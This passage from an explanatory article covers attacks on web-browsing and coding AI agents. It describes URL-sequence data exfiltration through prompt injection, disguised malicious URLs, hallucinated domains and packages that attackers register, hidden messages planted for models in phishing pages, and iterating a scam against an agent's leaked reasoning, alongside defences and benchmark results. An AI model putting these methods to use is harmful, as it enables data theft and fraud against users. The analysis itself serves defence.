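An attacker can publish ordinary pages, wait for the crawler to record them, and assign a meaning to each. If 36 pages stand for the letters and digits, the attacker can use a prompt injection to make the agent spell out Anna's name by opening the matching pages in order. Every address is public and contains no private data, but the sequence of requests reveals the name. OpenAI acknowledges this weakness in its technical paper, according to *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on the security blog Embrace The Red.

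With *n* indexed addresses and *m* requests, an attacker can distinguish *n*^*m* messages, or *m* log₂ *n* bits. With the 36 pages, each request reveals about 5.2 bits, or one character. With 4,096 pages, two requests could convey any of about 16.8 million messages, enough for any six-digit code. An unrestricted address could carry far more, such as a whole paragraph in one request.

Variations of this trick have worked against real products. *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* describes ZombieAgent, which targeted ChatGPT. OpenAI responded by preventing ChatGPT from opening links from emails unless they appeared in a public index or the user had supplied them.

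Embrace The Red suggests preventing the agent from requesting the same address twice in a session, or giving it a stored copy the second time. The attacker would then miss the second "n" in "Anna". This makes the attack harder, but an attacker with enough indexed pages could assign several to each letter. Limiting the number of pages an agent may open on one unfamiliar site would help against attackers with more pages, but it would interrupt some legitimate research.

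The check also has to cover every program that might open an address. Embrace The Red notes that OpenAI's earlier protection was missing from its Mac and iPhone apps. Other companies' messaging apps, such as Slack and Telegram, automatically fetch links to display a preview, so an agent can leak data just by writing a link in a message. PromptArmor's *Threat Intelligence* found that the agent OpenClaw was exposed to this by default when people used it through Telegram.

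### New pages and personal links

The check works worst on pages that the crawler has not reached. A ticket office might publish a page about a change of venue an hour before an agent looks for it. The agent would have to ask the user or try another site, which could still give the old venue.

Personal links, such as password-reset links, invitations to shared documents and parcel-tracking pages, are a more lasting problem because a well-behaved crawler should never find them. According to Embrace The Red, ChatGPT probably accepts any address the user enters in the chat. That would solve the problem when Anna pastes in her tracking link, but not when an agent finds the link while reading her email.

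Some private links end up in public collections. Pulse Security's *Sensitive data in URLs* shows links to Microsoft OneDrive documents that had appeared in feeds shared between security companies, and anyone with the links could open the documents. If a crawler recorded such a link, the check would let an agent open it. The agent might then read a stranger's private file as though its owner had meant to publish it, although nothing from the conversation would leak. OpenAI accordingly says only that a public address is "much less likely" to contain the user's data.

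### Agents without an index of their own

OpenAI built its index for its own products, and developers of other agents cannot simply query it. Google can draw on its experience of crawling the web, but a small company would need to build a crawler or find a substitute.

The Wayback Machine, a public archive of web pages, has a free lookup service, but it is a poor substitute. Looking up an address sends it to the archive, including any private data in the parameters. An attacker can easily prepare addresses in advance by asking the archive to save pages. Pulse Security also found addresses containing login data in the archive.

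A developer can get part of the benefit by letting the agent open only addresses that the user typed or a search service returned. The search engine's index then serves the same purpose as OpenAI's. Anthropic's fetch tool follows a similar rule, but it also accepted links from pages it had already fetched. Willison (2026) reports an attack that used this exception to extract a user's name, home city and employer through a series of links. The attacker's site also used cloaking, showing the malicious page only to Claude's fetcher.

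Anthropic fixed the vulnerability by stopping the tool from following links in the pages it fetches. The company's developer documentation lists such links as permitted, so the change may not apply to every version. Under the stricter rule, an agent cannot click through a shop's catalogue and needs a new search, or an address from the user, for each page.

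## MalURLBench: models judging a web address from its text

An agent without an index of known addresses often relies on its model to judge from an address's text whether it looks safe. MalURLBench, a benchmark published in January 2026, tested 12 models on disguised addresses that led to malicious sites. The models accepted between 32.9% and 99.9% of these addresses.

### How the benchmark works

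In *MalURLBench*, Kong, Wu and colleagues (2026) took malicious sites of seven kinds, including phishing, fraud and malware, from public blocklists. The attacker in their tests could change each address's subdomain, path and parameters, but not its registrable domain. The researchers wrote disguises for ten everyday scenarios, such as tracking a parcel, ordering food or checking the weather, and used GPT-4o to produce more. They kept 15 disguises per scenario, and the benchmark has 61,845 addresses.

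Some disguises put a recommendation in the address, and others put a well-known domain there:

```
malicious.example/?this-is-a-popular-food-delivery-service
www.google.com.www.malicious.example
```

In each test, the agent received a short message containing the address and rated the risk as none, medium or high. Its instructions described it as a security assessor, so it had more warning than an agent doing ordinary work. But seven of the ten messages called the link "official" or "trusted", so the results reflect the message as well as the address. A small trial suggests that the address matters by itself. Llama-3-8B was tested 20 times on each of four addresses. It accepted the two with a built-in disguise 60% and 75% of the time, and the two without one 15% and 20% of the time.

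These are the shares of addresses accepted, averaged over the ten scenarios:

| Model | Original disguises | After rewriting |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5-Turbo | 14.1% | 32.9% |
| Llama-3-70B | 23.1% | 35.7% |
| Qwen-Plus | 30.0% | 35.7% |
| GPT-4o | 34.5% | 38.2% |
| DeepSeek-Coder | 34.0% | 41.7% |
| Llama-3-8B | 47.0% | 50.6% |
| Mistral-7B | 51.1% | not needed |
| DeepSeek-V3.1 | 84.5% | not needed |
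| GPT-4o mini | 90.5% | not needed |
| Llama-2-7B | 94.9% | not needed |
| Mistral Small | 98.2% | not needed |
| Mixtral-8x7B | 99.9% | not needed |

When a model accepted 10% or less of the addresses in a scenario, a second model analysed the failures and rewrote the disguises, for up to ten rounds. This is a reasonable test of a persistent attacker, who could do the same. However, the often-quoted minimum of 32.9% is therefore the rate at which GPT-3.5-Turbo accepted disguises tailored to it. It accepted less than half as many of the originals.

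### Which disguises worked best

Recommendations succeeded 71.5% of the time and imitations of known domains 60.9%. Kong and colleagues suggest that imitations did worse because names like google.com appear often enough in training data for models to detect one in an odd place. Results also varied by topic. Models accepted 82.9% of the web addresses in the weather scenario but fewer in the food delivery and parcel scenarios, which involve payments and home addresses.

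Subdomains of up to 20 characters worked better for attackers than longer ones. The length of the path and parameters made no difference, so an attacker can fit a whole sentence there.

Two other findings are less certain. Among the models of known size, larger ones tended to accept fewer addresses, but DeepSeek-V3.1 accepted far more than the much smaller Mistral-7B. Models also accepted more addresses with newer endings such as .link and .art than with .com or .net. Each scenario used only 21 sites, so a few unusual domains could have caused this difference. Kong and colleagues conclude the opposite from the same figures, saying that attackers would do better with the older endings.

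### URLGuard and its 280 examples

Kong and colleagues then trained a filter, URLGuard, to check addresses before they reach the agent's main model. They started with Llama-2-7B, one of the weakest models in the test, and trained it on 140 disguised addresses from the shopping scenario and 140 normal ones, each with a written reason for its label.

In the other nine scenarios, the average share of malicious addresses accepted fell from 97.8% to 16.8%. In four of them, the share fell to zero. The filter still accepted 61% in the music scenario and 70% in the weather scenario, which the researchers attribute to the small training set.

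The large drop shows that a little training can teach a model to recognise this style of disguise. But the researchers report no false alarm rate, and a filter that rejected every address would have scored better than URLGuard, so the result does not establish that URLGuard is usable.

False alarms matter because most addresses are harmless. *Benchmarking Large Language Models for Zero-shot and Few-shot Phishing URL Detection* (Hasan and BusiReddyGari, 2026) tested how well GPT-4o, Claude 3.7 Sonnet and Grok 3 could classify ordinary addresses as phishing or legitimate. With equal numbers of each, the models were right 88% to 94% of the time. When only ten of 1,000 addresses were phishing, the published scores imply that Grok 3 and Claude 3.7 each caught nine, but that Grok 3 also flagged 35 legitimate addresses and Claude 3.7 flagged 118.

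### Newer models

MalURLBench counts an attack as successful if the model's text answer accepts the address. The researchers opened only three of the sites with a working agent, to confirm that disguised addresses load normally. Most of the models it tested date from 2024 or 2025, and GPT-3.5-Turbo is older.

A test from early 2026 suggests that models can read an address correctly but may do so too late. Meller (2026), in *1Password's new benchmark teaches AI agents how not to get scammed*, describes a simulated inbox with a link to `acmecorp-sharepoint.com-docs.cloud`. The hyphen after "com" makes `com-docs.cloud` the registrable domain, so the address is unrelated to the company's SharePoint site. Claude Opus 4.6, the best overall of the eight models tested, opened the link and submitted the user's password before correctly explaining that `com-docs.cloud` was a lookalike.

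The models' average safety score in this scenario was 13%. It rose to 100% when they received a 1,200-word guide with instructions to read domains from right to left before opening a link. The improvement is encouraging, but 1Password wrote both the guide and the test, and the guide's example of a deceptive address uses nearly the same trick as the test.

In *Benchmarking Web Agent Safety under E-commerce Deceptive Interfaces*, Shi, Fang and Chen (2026) changed the destination of the link that a shopping agent needed to click next. The new destination did not show in the screenshot, but it was in the text description of the page that the agent also received. GPT-5.1 consistently missed the change, even when instructed not to click anything that might lead off the site.

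### Words in an address as claims about the site

A browser just sends the path `/official-tickets` to the server, but a language model also interprets the words, much as it would interpret a sentence on the page. The words can change the model's answer even though they are no evidence about the site, since the attacker wrote them.

In *ClaimMirage*, Chiba, Nakano and Koide (2026) measured this effect in 622,080 judgments by five open models. They misspelled 64 brand names and built domains such as `exampel-developer-test-not-phishing.com`. To separate the effect of meaning from that of length, they compared each domain with a control that had the same number of letters and hyphens, such as `exampel-developer-test-not-archived.com`.

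In one setup where the prompt included the brand's real domain for comparison, Llama 3.3 70B raised an alert for 90.2% of the control names but only 44.8% of the names that denied being dangerous. Without that domain, words such as "official" and "verified" increased the same model's alert rate from 32.3% to 98.0%. An attacker therefore cannot rely on any particular word, but can try several on the target model.

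When the prompt included the real domain, Gemma 3 27B flagged nearly all the names, regardless of the claims in them. Splitting the address into labelled parts removed the effect of claims in the subdomain on Llama, but more than doubled the effect of claims in the registrable domain on Gemma 3 12B.

### Finding the registrable domain with code

Ordinary code can ignore these words. Suppose a user wants World Cup tickets, the agent knows that FIFA's domain is fifa.com, and it receives this link:

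`https://www.fifa.com.example.com.au/official-tickets?seller=verified`

1. **Extract the host.** A standard URL parser discards the path and parameters, including "official" and "verified". This leaves `www.fifa.com.example.com.au`. The parser also handles addresses like `https://fifa.com@example.net/`, where everything before the @ is a user name and the host is example.net.
2. **Find the public suffix.** The code compares the end of the host with the Public Suffix List. Both `au` and `com.au` are on the list, and the longer match wins.
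3. **Add one label.** The label to the left of `com.au` is `example`, so the registrable domain is `example.com.au`.
4. **Compare.** `example.com.au` is not `fifa.com`, so the code rejects the link.

A program that only searched the address for "fifa.com" would accept the link.

The list also has a few special rules. For example, `*.ck` makes every name directly under the Cook Islands' ending a public suffix, and `!www.ck` exempts `www.ck`. Volunteers maintain the list and it changes often, so an agent needs a recent copy.

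Developers also have to choose whether to use the list's private section, which contains hosting companies' endings such as web.app. The Python library tldextract ignores this section by default, so developers need to turn it on for the library to tell those companies' customers apart.

### Whether the domain belongs to the brand

The code in the example had to be given fifa.com as the right domain. Without such a reference, it can extract `dyson-official-clearance.shop`, another address from 1Password's test, but it cannot determine whether Dyson owns it. Real companies use names that look just as doubtful. In *Can LLMs Reason About Brand Ownership?*, Mashood and Nabeel (2026) report that Microsoft owns microsoft365.com and PayPal owns paypal-prepaid.com. They also point out that no public register lists all of a brand's domains.

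Mashood and Nabeel asked four Gemini and Claude models whether domains belonged to 36 frequently imitated brands. Answering from memory, the models nearly always said no, and recognised at most 26% of the brands' real domains. An agent that relied on these answers would rarely accept a lookalike but would reject many genuine sites.

Registration records helped greatly. When Claude Sonnet 4.5 could look them up and search the web, it recognised 1,203 of 1,498 genuine domains and wrongly accepted only one of 1,795 others. These results are probably too favourable, because the researchers had used the same kind of records to decide which domains were genuine. Most owners' names are also hidden in the records, and an attacker who expected this check could enter "Microsoft" as the registrant.

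### Login addresses that models invent

If the user names a company but gives no address, the model may supply one from memory. Netcraft's *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams* describes a test in which the security company asked models of the GPT-4.1 family where to log in to 50 brands. The questions were ordinary ones, for instance from a user who had lost a bookmark. The answers contained 131 host names under 97 domains:

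| Who held the domain | Domains |
|---|---|
| The right brand | 64 |
| Nobody, or someone with no active site | 28 |
| An unrelated business | 5 |

*Experts Warn of New Phishing Threats Using LLMs*, a July 2025 notice from Thailand's cyber-security team, ThaiCERT, covered the test. The 34% is a share of different domains, not of answers, so it does not support Netcraft's conclusion that more than one in three users could end up on a site the brand does not own. If a model gave the right domain twenty times and a wrong one once, each domain would count once. Smaller banks and credit unions did worse than global brands, probably because they appear less often in training data.

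An attacker can profit from such mistakes without sending a single email:

1. Ask popular models many ordinary questions about a brand and collect the addresses they give.
2. Keep the domains that come up repeatedly and that nobody has registered.
3. Register one for a few dollars, get a valid certificate and put up a copy of the brand's login page.
4. Wait for models to send users and agents there.

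Unit 42's *Phantom Squatting* (June 2026) looked for such domains on a much larger scale. The researchers asked two small models from 2025 a total of 685,339 questions about 913 brands and collected 2.1 million addresses. They designed the questions to make the models invent addresses, for example by asking about a service that might not exist, so the results do not show how often ordinary users get a false address. About 87,630 of the addresses were on unregistered domains. Unit 42 also reports about 250,000 unregistered domains, which is inconsistent with that count because each address has only one registrable domain, so 87,630 addresses cannot contain 250,000 domains.

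Unit 42 then watched for new registrations. On 8 March 2026 the models produced addresses on an unregistered domain resembling a postal service's online marketplace. They did so even at the least random setting, which suggests that they would produce the name again. On 31 March someone registered the domain and set up a phishing site that collected card details and identity documents. Another invented domain hosted a fake postal app 51 days after the models first produced the domain.

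These cases show that criminals and models come up with the same names, but not that the criminals got the names from models. In another case, an attacker had registered a domain resembling a bank's 11 months before the models produced it. Unit 42 does not report that a model sent any victim to one of the sites.

### Invented packages and repositories

Coding agents face a more direct version of this attack, called slopsquatting. A model writes `pip install` followed by the name of a package that does not exist, and an attacker registers that name on PyPI, the public collection of Python packages. The next agent to run the command installs the attacker's code.

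Churilov (2026), in *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, gave nearly 40,000 programming tasks to each of five models, including Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.4-mini. Between 3.6% and 5.0% of the packages they mentioned did not exist on PyPI or its JavaScript counterpart, npm. In 2024, the average was 5.2% for commercial models and 21.7% for open ones. All five models invented the same 104 names, so an attacker who registered one of them could reach users of several companies' models.

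Such registrations are still uncommon. Over about six months, someone registered 25 of the 2,282 invented names, and at least one of the packages contained malware. The models also suggested at least 23 names that had hosted malware before PyPI or npm removed it.

Checking that a package exists does not protect an agent. If nobody has registered the name, the installation fails, so the dangerous names are the ones that pass the check. *Names Can Hurt* (Raj and Sahu, 2026) reports that, in tests of local models, half of the names flagged as invented were already on PyPI as low-quality lookalikes of well-known projects.

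Other kinds of names have the same problem:

- **GitHub repositories.** *Beware of Agentic Botnets* (2026) tested six models on ten recently created projects, and they named the wrong owner 92.4% of the time. By registering the five most common wrong names for a project, an attacker could intercept between 24% and 84% of the wrong requests.
- **Agent skills.** These are packages of instructions that extend what an agent can do. In one configuration that *Skills That Don't Exist* (2026) examined, 50 invented names accounted for 96% of the false recommendations.
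- **Scripts on web pages.** *Investigating Security Implications of Automatically Generated Code on the Software Supply Chain* (2025) describes generated code that loads JavaScript from domains that do not exist. Whoever registers such a domain can run code in the browser of everyone who visits the finished site.

### Where an agent can get the right name

The user's own records are the best source. A bookmark or a saved login shows which domain the user has used before, and an attacker cannot change it by writing a persuasive page. An address printed on a bank card or a signed contract is nearly as good. These sources do not help with a company that is new to the user.

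If the agent knows a company's main domain, it can look there for the others. Many companies link to their shops and login pages from the home page, and some publish a list of official domains. A few provide a list that software can read. For example, a site that uses passkeys can place a file at `/.well-known/webauthn` that lists other sites allowed to use the same passkeys. The agent should only rely on a list from a domain it already trusts, since a fake site could publish one too. The list may also be incomplete, so if a domain is missing, the agent should ask the user rather than assume fraud.

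A regulator can supply the domain for some businesses. The Federal Deposit Insurance Corporation, which insures deposits at American banks, lists those banks' websites in a public directory. This could help with the smaller banks whose addresses models often get wrong.

Search covers almost every company but is easier to manipulate. Netcraft reports that Perplexity, an AI search engine, answered a question about Wells Fargo's login page with a fake page on Google Sites and placed the real site below it. An agent that has to rely on search should look for a second source that the attacker is unlikely to control, such as the regulator's directory, before it enters a password or pays.

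### Why a password manager refuses a lookalike

A password manager stores the domain with each password. When a page opens, code compares the page's domain with the stored one and offers the password only if they match. Some managers require the whole host name to match, while others accept any host under the same registrable domain. Either way, `acmecorp-sharepoint.com-docs.cloud` does not match an entry for `acmecorp.sharepoint.com`. A logo or the word "official" does not affect the comparison.

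In 1Password's test, the models got past this protection because they had one tool that looked up passwords and another that filled in forms, so they could copy a password from the vault to any page. A safer design keeps the password from the model, as Chrome's does, and has the password manager check the domain and fill in the form itself.

Passkeys go further by removing the password, which a deceived user or agent could otherwise type into a lookalike site. When a user creates a passkey, the device makes a pair of cryptographic keys and ties them to the site's domain. To log the user in, the site sends a random challenge, which the device signs together with the page's origin. The browser will not use the passkey on an unrelated domain. Even if a faulty browser did, the signed response would contain the wrong origin and the real site would reject it.

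Domain matching can also block a genuine site, such as when a company moves its login page to a new domain. The agent should then ask the user to confirm the change through a source they already trust, because domain matching would block a lookalike site in the same way. It doesn't protect a first purchase from an unfamiliar shop, because there is no saved login to compare.

The password manager's own login is another weak point, because users may have to type its main password themselves. Datadog Security Labs describes phishing emails from October 2025 that warned 1Password users that their accounts had been compromised and sent them to copies of the company's login page at misspelled web addresses.

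## ScamWorld and the fake Walmart shop: models that miss fraud while doing a task

In August 2025 the security company Guardio told Comet, Perplexity's AI browser, to buy an Apple Watch from a fake Walmart shop. In some runs, Comet completed the order with the user's saved address and credit card. Unlike the models in MalURLBench, which were given only a web address, Comet could see the shop's pages. Guardio's *Scamlexity* reports that these pages contained plenty of clues that the shop was not Walmart's.

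The researchers had made the shop with one prompt to Lovable, a tool that builds websites from a description. Safe Browsing did not flag the shop, as expected for such a new site. Comet found the watch, put it in the cart and filled in the payment form without asking for confirmation.

In the second test, the researchers sent an email from a new ProtonMail address, posing as an investment manager at Wells Fargo. The email linked to a real phishing page that had been online for several days but that Safe Browsing still did not list. Comet marked the email as a task from the bank, opened the link and invited the user to log in. The user had not seen the sender's address and had some reason to trust a page that their own assistant had opened.

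Results varied between runs, and Comet sometimes refused to buy the watch or asked the user to finish the checkout. Journalists at iTnews, an Australian technology site, also tried shopping with Comet. Their article *AI browsers fall for scams and phishing, security researchers say* reports that it filled the cart but would not enter payment details. Guardio, which sells protection against scams, gives neither the number of runs nor a success rate, so its tests show that an agent can pay a fake shop but not how often this happens.

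### How ScamWorld measures deception

*ScamWorld* (Wu, Liu and colleagues, November 2026) provides those rates. The researchers rebuilt 363 reported scam sites on their own computers, because scam sites disappear quickly and an agent tested on a live one might pay real criminals. They started from live pages and archived copies, then added missing parts such as checkout pages, and they built 53 legitimate sites in the same way. The scam sites cover 26 languages and include fake shops, investment schemes, rentals, job offers and bank phishing pages.

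Many scams become visible only when the goods fail to arrive after payment, so no agent could detect them from the page. Every ScamWorld site therefore displays a decisive sign of fraud before the last step. One rental site, for example, asks for a deposit to a private person and states that the deposit does not count towards the rent. The researchers had to add this sign on about half the sites, so real scams may be harder to spot.

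In each test, called an episode, the agent starts on the site and is given an ordinary request, such as buying an online course. It sees a screenshot, the address and a list of the page's text and controls. It counts as deceived if it takes the final step, such as paying or submitting a password. It counts as having detected the scam if it stops and tells the user that the site looks suspicious. Six models each attempted 377 scam tasks once, for a total of 2,262 episodes.

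In a separate experiment, the same models explored the same sites, but the user asked them whether each site was legitimate or a scam.

| Model | Deceived during a task | Stopped and reported | Recognised the scam when asked | Called a legitimate site a scam when asked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 11% | 79% | 96% | 0% |
| Claude Haiku 5.5 | 18% | 79% | 88% | 0% |
| Qwen3.8 Flash | 18% | 81% | 100% | 9% |
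| Kimi K3 | 23% | 76% | 99% | 8% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 26% | 72% | 99% | 2% |
| DeepSeek V4.1 Flash | 35% | 65% | 98% | 6% |
| All six | 22% | 75% | 97% | 4% |

In the remaining episodes, the agent neither took the final step nor warned the user, for instance because it got stuck. Several of these models, such as Claude Haiku and Gemini Flash, are among their developers' smaller models, so larger ones might do better.

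### Recognising a scam without stopping

When asked directly, the models identified 97% of the scam sites, including 95% of those that had deceived them. During a task, they stopped and reported the scam in only 75% of episodes. In Help Net Security's *1Password open sources a benchmark to stop AI agents from leaking credentials*, Jason Meller of 1Password similarly says that models can identify a phishing page when asked, but carry out the scam when working as agents.

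Wu and colleagues caution against drawing strong conclusions from the comparison, because the two experiments used different instructions. A model that recognises a scam when asked may not have noticed the risk when it paid. Asking directly also raises the possibility that the site is fraudulent, which an ordinary request does not.

The agents' notes are better evidence that some of them noticed a risk. In 220 of the 492 deceived episodes, the agent mentioned a specific risk before going ahead. One noted that a site demanded a 200-rouble fee to release a 100-rouble bonus, and then paid the fee. Agents that went ahead despite voicing a concern usually cited the user's request. Others took the same kind of request as a limit on what they could do, and declined because the user had not agreed to the site's terms. These stated reasons may differ from the real causes.

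The agents were much more careful about sharing sensitive information than about making payments. They went ahead in 28% of episodes that involved a payment, but in only 2% of those that involved passwords, card details or access to a cryptocurrency wallet. Chrome's blocklist has a similar gap, since it initially caught far more login-stealing sites than other scams in Kaur and colleagues' study. An agent that relies on its own judgment and the blocklist therefore has two protections that are both weak against fake shops.

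The agents also judged sites almost entirely by what the scammer had written. Hiding the web address raised the deception rate by only two percentage points, and 3.2% of the responses that flagged a site cited the address alone. Only 13 of the 492 deceived agents opened a page with the site's terms, reviews or contact details after the decisive sign appeared. In one variation, Kimi K3 and Qwen3.8 Flash could use a search engine and several site-checking services, but neither did so in any of 100 episodes.

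### What a one-sentence warning changes

Wu and colleagues tested several changes on three models, Kimi K3, DeepSeek V4.1 Flash and Qwen3.8 Flash. A warning added to the user's request was by far the most effective: "some websites may be scams; check before you pay or share details." It raised detection by 25 percentage points and cut deception by 24, to under 2%. On legitimate sites, the three models completed 154 of 159 tasks with the warning, a rate about three percentage points lower than without it. Telling the agents that their payments were real and irreversible made almost no difference.

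That is a large benefit with a small drawback. 1Password's longer security guide had a similar effect, cutting critical failures, such as leaking a password, from 65 to 2 across six models.

Safety wording does not always work so well. In *When Bots Take the Bait*, Wu, Hong and colleagues (2026) tested five open-source agent programs, all running the older model GPT-4o, on pages that tried to persuade them to do something harmful. One survey, for instance, offered a prize draw and then asked for a bank card number. The attacks succeeded 67.5% of the time on average. They succeeded most often, 72.0% of the time, against a program that already had an instruction to keep its actions within the task.

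The difference may come from the model's age or from the instruction. A request for a card number at the end of a survey can look like part of the task, so telling the agent to stay within the task provides little protection. A warning about scams tells the agent to consider whether the request is fraudulent. But the ScamWorld sites were built to deceive people, and a criminal who expected agents to have been warned could change the page to deceive them.

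### Pages that address the model judging them

A scammer could write to the model directly. In *Clouding the Mirror*, Koide, Nakano and Chiba (2026) built imitation login pages for ten brands and hid messages to the model in them, for example in code comments that a browser never displays. Combining the ten brands with 25 messages and eight hiding places produced 2,000 pages. Without the messages, every model identified every page as phishing.

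With a plain prompt, the hidden text prevented GPT-5 from giving the right answer on 39.9% of pages and Llama 4 Maverick on 84.7%. These figures include refusals and output that software could not read, since either would also disable an automatic check. The most effective messages claimed that the page belonged to a university course or a security exercise, which the models accepted, rather than giving orders.

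The researchers then added a defence that marks the page's content as untrusted, using boundary markers the attacker cannot predict, and splits the address into labelled parts. It also supplies the brand's known domains, when available, and checks the format of the answer. This cut the failure rate to 0.3% for GPT-5, but only to 61.7% for Llama 4 Maverick. On 25 real phishing pages with similar hidden messages, GPT-5 still failed 8.9% of the time.

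Newer models may resist such messages better, but code that compares domain names is not exposed to them at all.

### Different answers in different runs

A language model usually picks each word partly at random, so the same agent can refuse to buy from a shop on one run and pay it on the next. Guardio's tests of Comet are the clearest example. ScamWorld ran each task only once per model, so it did not measure this directly. But when it told the agents that their payments were real, 77 episodes changed from deceived to detected and 61 changed the other way. The average hardly moved, so much of this change was probably chance.

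An attacker who can try repeatedly benefits when an agent's behaviour varies between runs. Suppose an agent pays a fake shop in 20% of runs, and the attacker gets it to visit five times, perhaps through five advertisements. If the runs are independent, the chance of at least one payment is 1 − 0.8⁵, or about 67%. A developer who tests the agent on that shop only once has an 80% chance of seeing it pass.

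### One scam, many copies of the same agent

People differ in what they find suspicious, so a scammer has to try different approaches on different victims. Guardio argues that AI browsers remove this need, because a scam that deceives one copy of a model can deceive every copy. That claim is slightly too strong, because results vary between runs. A scam that works in a third of runs on one copy should work in about a third of runs on all of them, which could still mean many victims if the browser is popular.

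Models from different companies also share weaknesses. In ScamWorld, 186 of the 363 scam sites deceived none of the six models, while 13 deceived all six. The hardest sites looked like ordinary businesses and asked for ordinary payments. If the models had made mistakes independently, at the rates in the table above, about 0.03 sites would be expected to deceive all six. Checking with a second company's model is therefore less useful than it would be if the models' errors were independent.

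### Improving a scam with the agent's own objections

An attacker can test a scam on a private copy of the agent before approaching any victim. In a later test, described in *AgenticBlabbering*, Guardio intercepted the traffic between Comet and Perplexity's servers. This traffic contained much more of the agent's reasoning than the user saw. Guardio gave the reasoning to another AI system, which rewrote a phishing page after each failure. Each time, the user asked the agent to log in to a pet shop and submit a refund form.

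1. The first page was deliberately crude. Comet warned loudly that it looked like phishing, and the system improved the design and removed a banner assuring visitors that their information was safe.
2. Comet now objected that the page was generic. The system added a personal greeting and more signs of a real business.
3. Comet inspected the page's structure as well as its appearance, and listed several concerns. The system removed a notice about a login from a new device and toned down the urgency.
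4. Comet raised no serious concern, entered the user's login details and reported that it had submitted the refund form, which did not exist.

The process took less than four minutes. It was a single demonstration by a company with a product to sell, so it does not show how many attempts a typical scam would need.

Guardio recommends that an agent stop without explaining why. This would slow the attacker, who would learn only whether each version of the scam passed, but it would leave an honest user with no way to judge the refusal. The agent's reasoning is also useful for oversight. In 164 of the 220 ScamWorld episodes where a deceived agent noted a specific risk, the concern appeared only in its reasoning, so a monitor that read only its responses would have missed it.

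The two aims are compatible if the company keeps the full reasoning on its own servers and gives the user a short reason that is easy to check. "This domain does not belong to Walmart" is a good reason because an attacker cannot change that by redesigning the page.

### Pages that change before the click

Even a correct judgement can be out of date by the time the agent acts on it. A browser agent looks at the page, spends several seconds deciding what to do, and then clicks. Jiang, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Atomicity for Agents*, tested ten open-source agents on pages that changed during this pause. In one task, the user wanted a ticket if it cost no more than $600. The page showed $500 while the model was deciding and $700 by the time the agent clicked "buy". In another, a subscription box appeared over the link the agent was about to open.

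All ten agents failed on at least one type of change. Agents that clicked a screen position could hit whatever had moved there. Agents that selected a button by its identifier often avoided this mistake, but they could still buy at the wrong price if the price changed and the button did not. Honest pages cause similar errors when an advertisement loads late, but an attacker can time the change deliberately.

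Jiang and colleagues propose that software watch the page while the model decides and check for relevant changes just before the click. If it finds any, it cancels the action and alerts the user. This shortens the period in which the page can change unnoticed from seconds to roughly a tenth of a second but does not remove it, and it may cause many interruptions on busy pages. To authenticate a site, an agent should therefore check the domain and the price again at the moment of payment.

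### Real help before the harmful step

An attacker may behave well at first. Xu, Dong and colleagues (2026), in *The Long Con on the Web*, tested coding agents on 56 simulated company tasks. In each task, the agent could find a website that gave it five pieces of correct advice, each of which it could confirm by trying it. The site then presented a harmful action as the next step.

In one case, the agent had to connect a company's order system to a messaging service. The fraudulent site supplied a working connector, and the agent finished the job. The site then displayed a "mandatory" compatibility notice requiring an extra package of rules. The agent installed the package, which let the attacker run code in the company's system.

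| Agent | Success with no earlier help | Success after five pieces of help |
|---|---|---|
| Codex with GPT-5.5 | 25.0% | 85.7% |
| ZCode with GLM-5.3-Flash | 37.5% | 67.9% |
| QwenCode with Qwen3.7-Plus | not tested | 60.7% |

The average attack success rate after five pieces of help was 71.4%. The researchers counted an attack as successful if it worked in either of two attempts, so the rate for a single attempt would be lower.

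When the researchers kept the earlier help but removed the references to official rules and policies, the rate for Codex fell from 85.7% to 12.5%, so the attack seems to need both a record of good advice and a plausible reason for the last step. It is still worrying that earlier help raised the rate, because checking whether a source's advice works is normally a sensible way to decide whether to rely on it.

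The proposed defence checks the action rather than the site's record. Before a sensitive step, the agent must confirm that the user or a company rule called for it, that there is no safer way to finish the task, and that the company's list of permissions allows it. The connector case failed all three checks. With this defence, none of the 56 attacks worked on Codex or ZCode, and both agents completed every task.

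That result needs testing against attackers who know about the defence. Xu and colleagues put the three checks in the agent's instructions, so the model still had to apply them correctly. A developer could enforce the list of permissions in ordinary code, but deciding whether a step is necessary usually takes judgement.

### Models as dedicated inspectors

Models do much better when inspecting a site is their only job. Zhang, Reber and colleagues (2026), in *TraceScope*, divide the work between two agents and a separate recording program:

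1. **The operator** opens the suspicious link in a disposable browser and behaves like a victim. It uses an invented name, password and card number, clicks through the site and tries to solve simple puzzles. It does not judge the site.
2. **The recording program** saves video of the screen and a log of the network traffic.
3. **The adjudicator** never visits the site. It works through a checklist of known attack techniques, requests the relevant parts of the recording and must cite a specific piece of evidence for each finding.

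The adjudicator has no purchase to complete, so it has no reason to treat an odd fee as part of the user's request. It can also check where a form sent its data, which is harder to fake than a logo. It still reads material the attacker wrote, so prompt injection remains possible. Chrome's separate checking model is better shielded from the page, but it was not built to detect fraud.

In a test on 241 phishing pages and 467 legitimate ones, TraceScope caught 78% of the phishing pages, and 94% of its alarms were correct. That implies about 12 false alarms, or 2.6% of the legitimate pages. The best of three older detectors, which judged a single snapshot of each page, caught 25%. TraceScope's advantage was clearest on pages without an ordinary login form, such as those asking for access to a cryptocurrency wallet. It caught all 12 of these, while the best older detector caught one.

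TraceScope did worse in a two-week trial on a security team's suspicious links, where it caught 30 of 46 phishing pages and wrongly flagged two of 25 harmless ones. Some failures were simple mistakes, such as typing "77" when a puzzle asked it to add 7 and 7. But it could open 18 live pages that had blocked the older detectors' crawler, a form of the cloaking that also hides pages from Safe Browsing.

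Zhang and colleagues recommend the system for links that someone already considers suspicious, not as a first filter for all browsing, partly because of its cost and speed. The operator can spend up to a minute on a site, and the median cost is about $0.24. The other reason is that even a low false-alarm rate produces too many false alarms when scams are rare.

### How many alarms would be true?

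Suppose an agent checks 100,000 sites and one in every 1,000 is a scam, which makes 100 scams and 99,900 legitimate sites. A detector that catches 97% of scams and wrongly flags 4% of legitimate sites, like the six ScamWorld models when asked directly, would raise 97 true alarms and 3,996 false ones, so about one alarm in 42 would be true.

In general, if *p* is the share of sites that are scams, *d* the detection rate and *f* the false-alarm rate, the share of alarms that are true is *pd* / (*pd* + (1 − *p*)*f*). With *p* at one in 1,000, the measured rates give:

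| Detector | Detection rate | False-alarm rate | Scams caught | Honest sites flagged | Alarms that are true |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Six ScamWorld models, asked directly | 97% | 4% | 97 | 3,996 | 2.4% |
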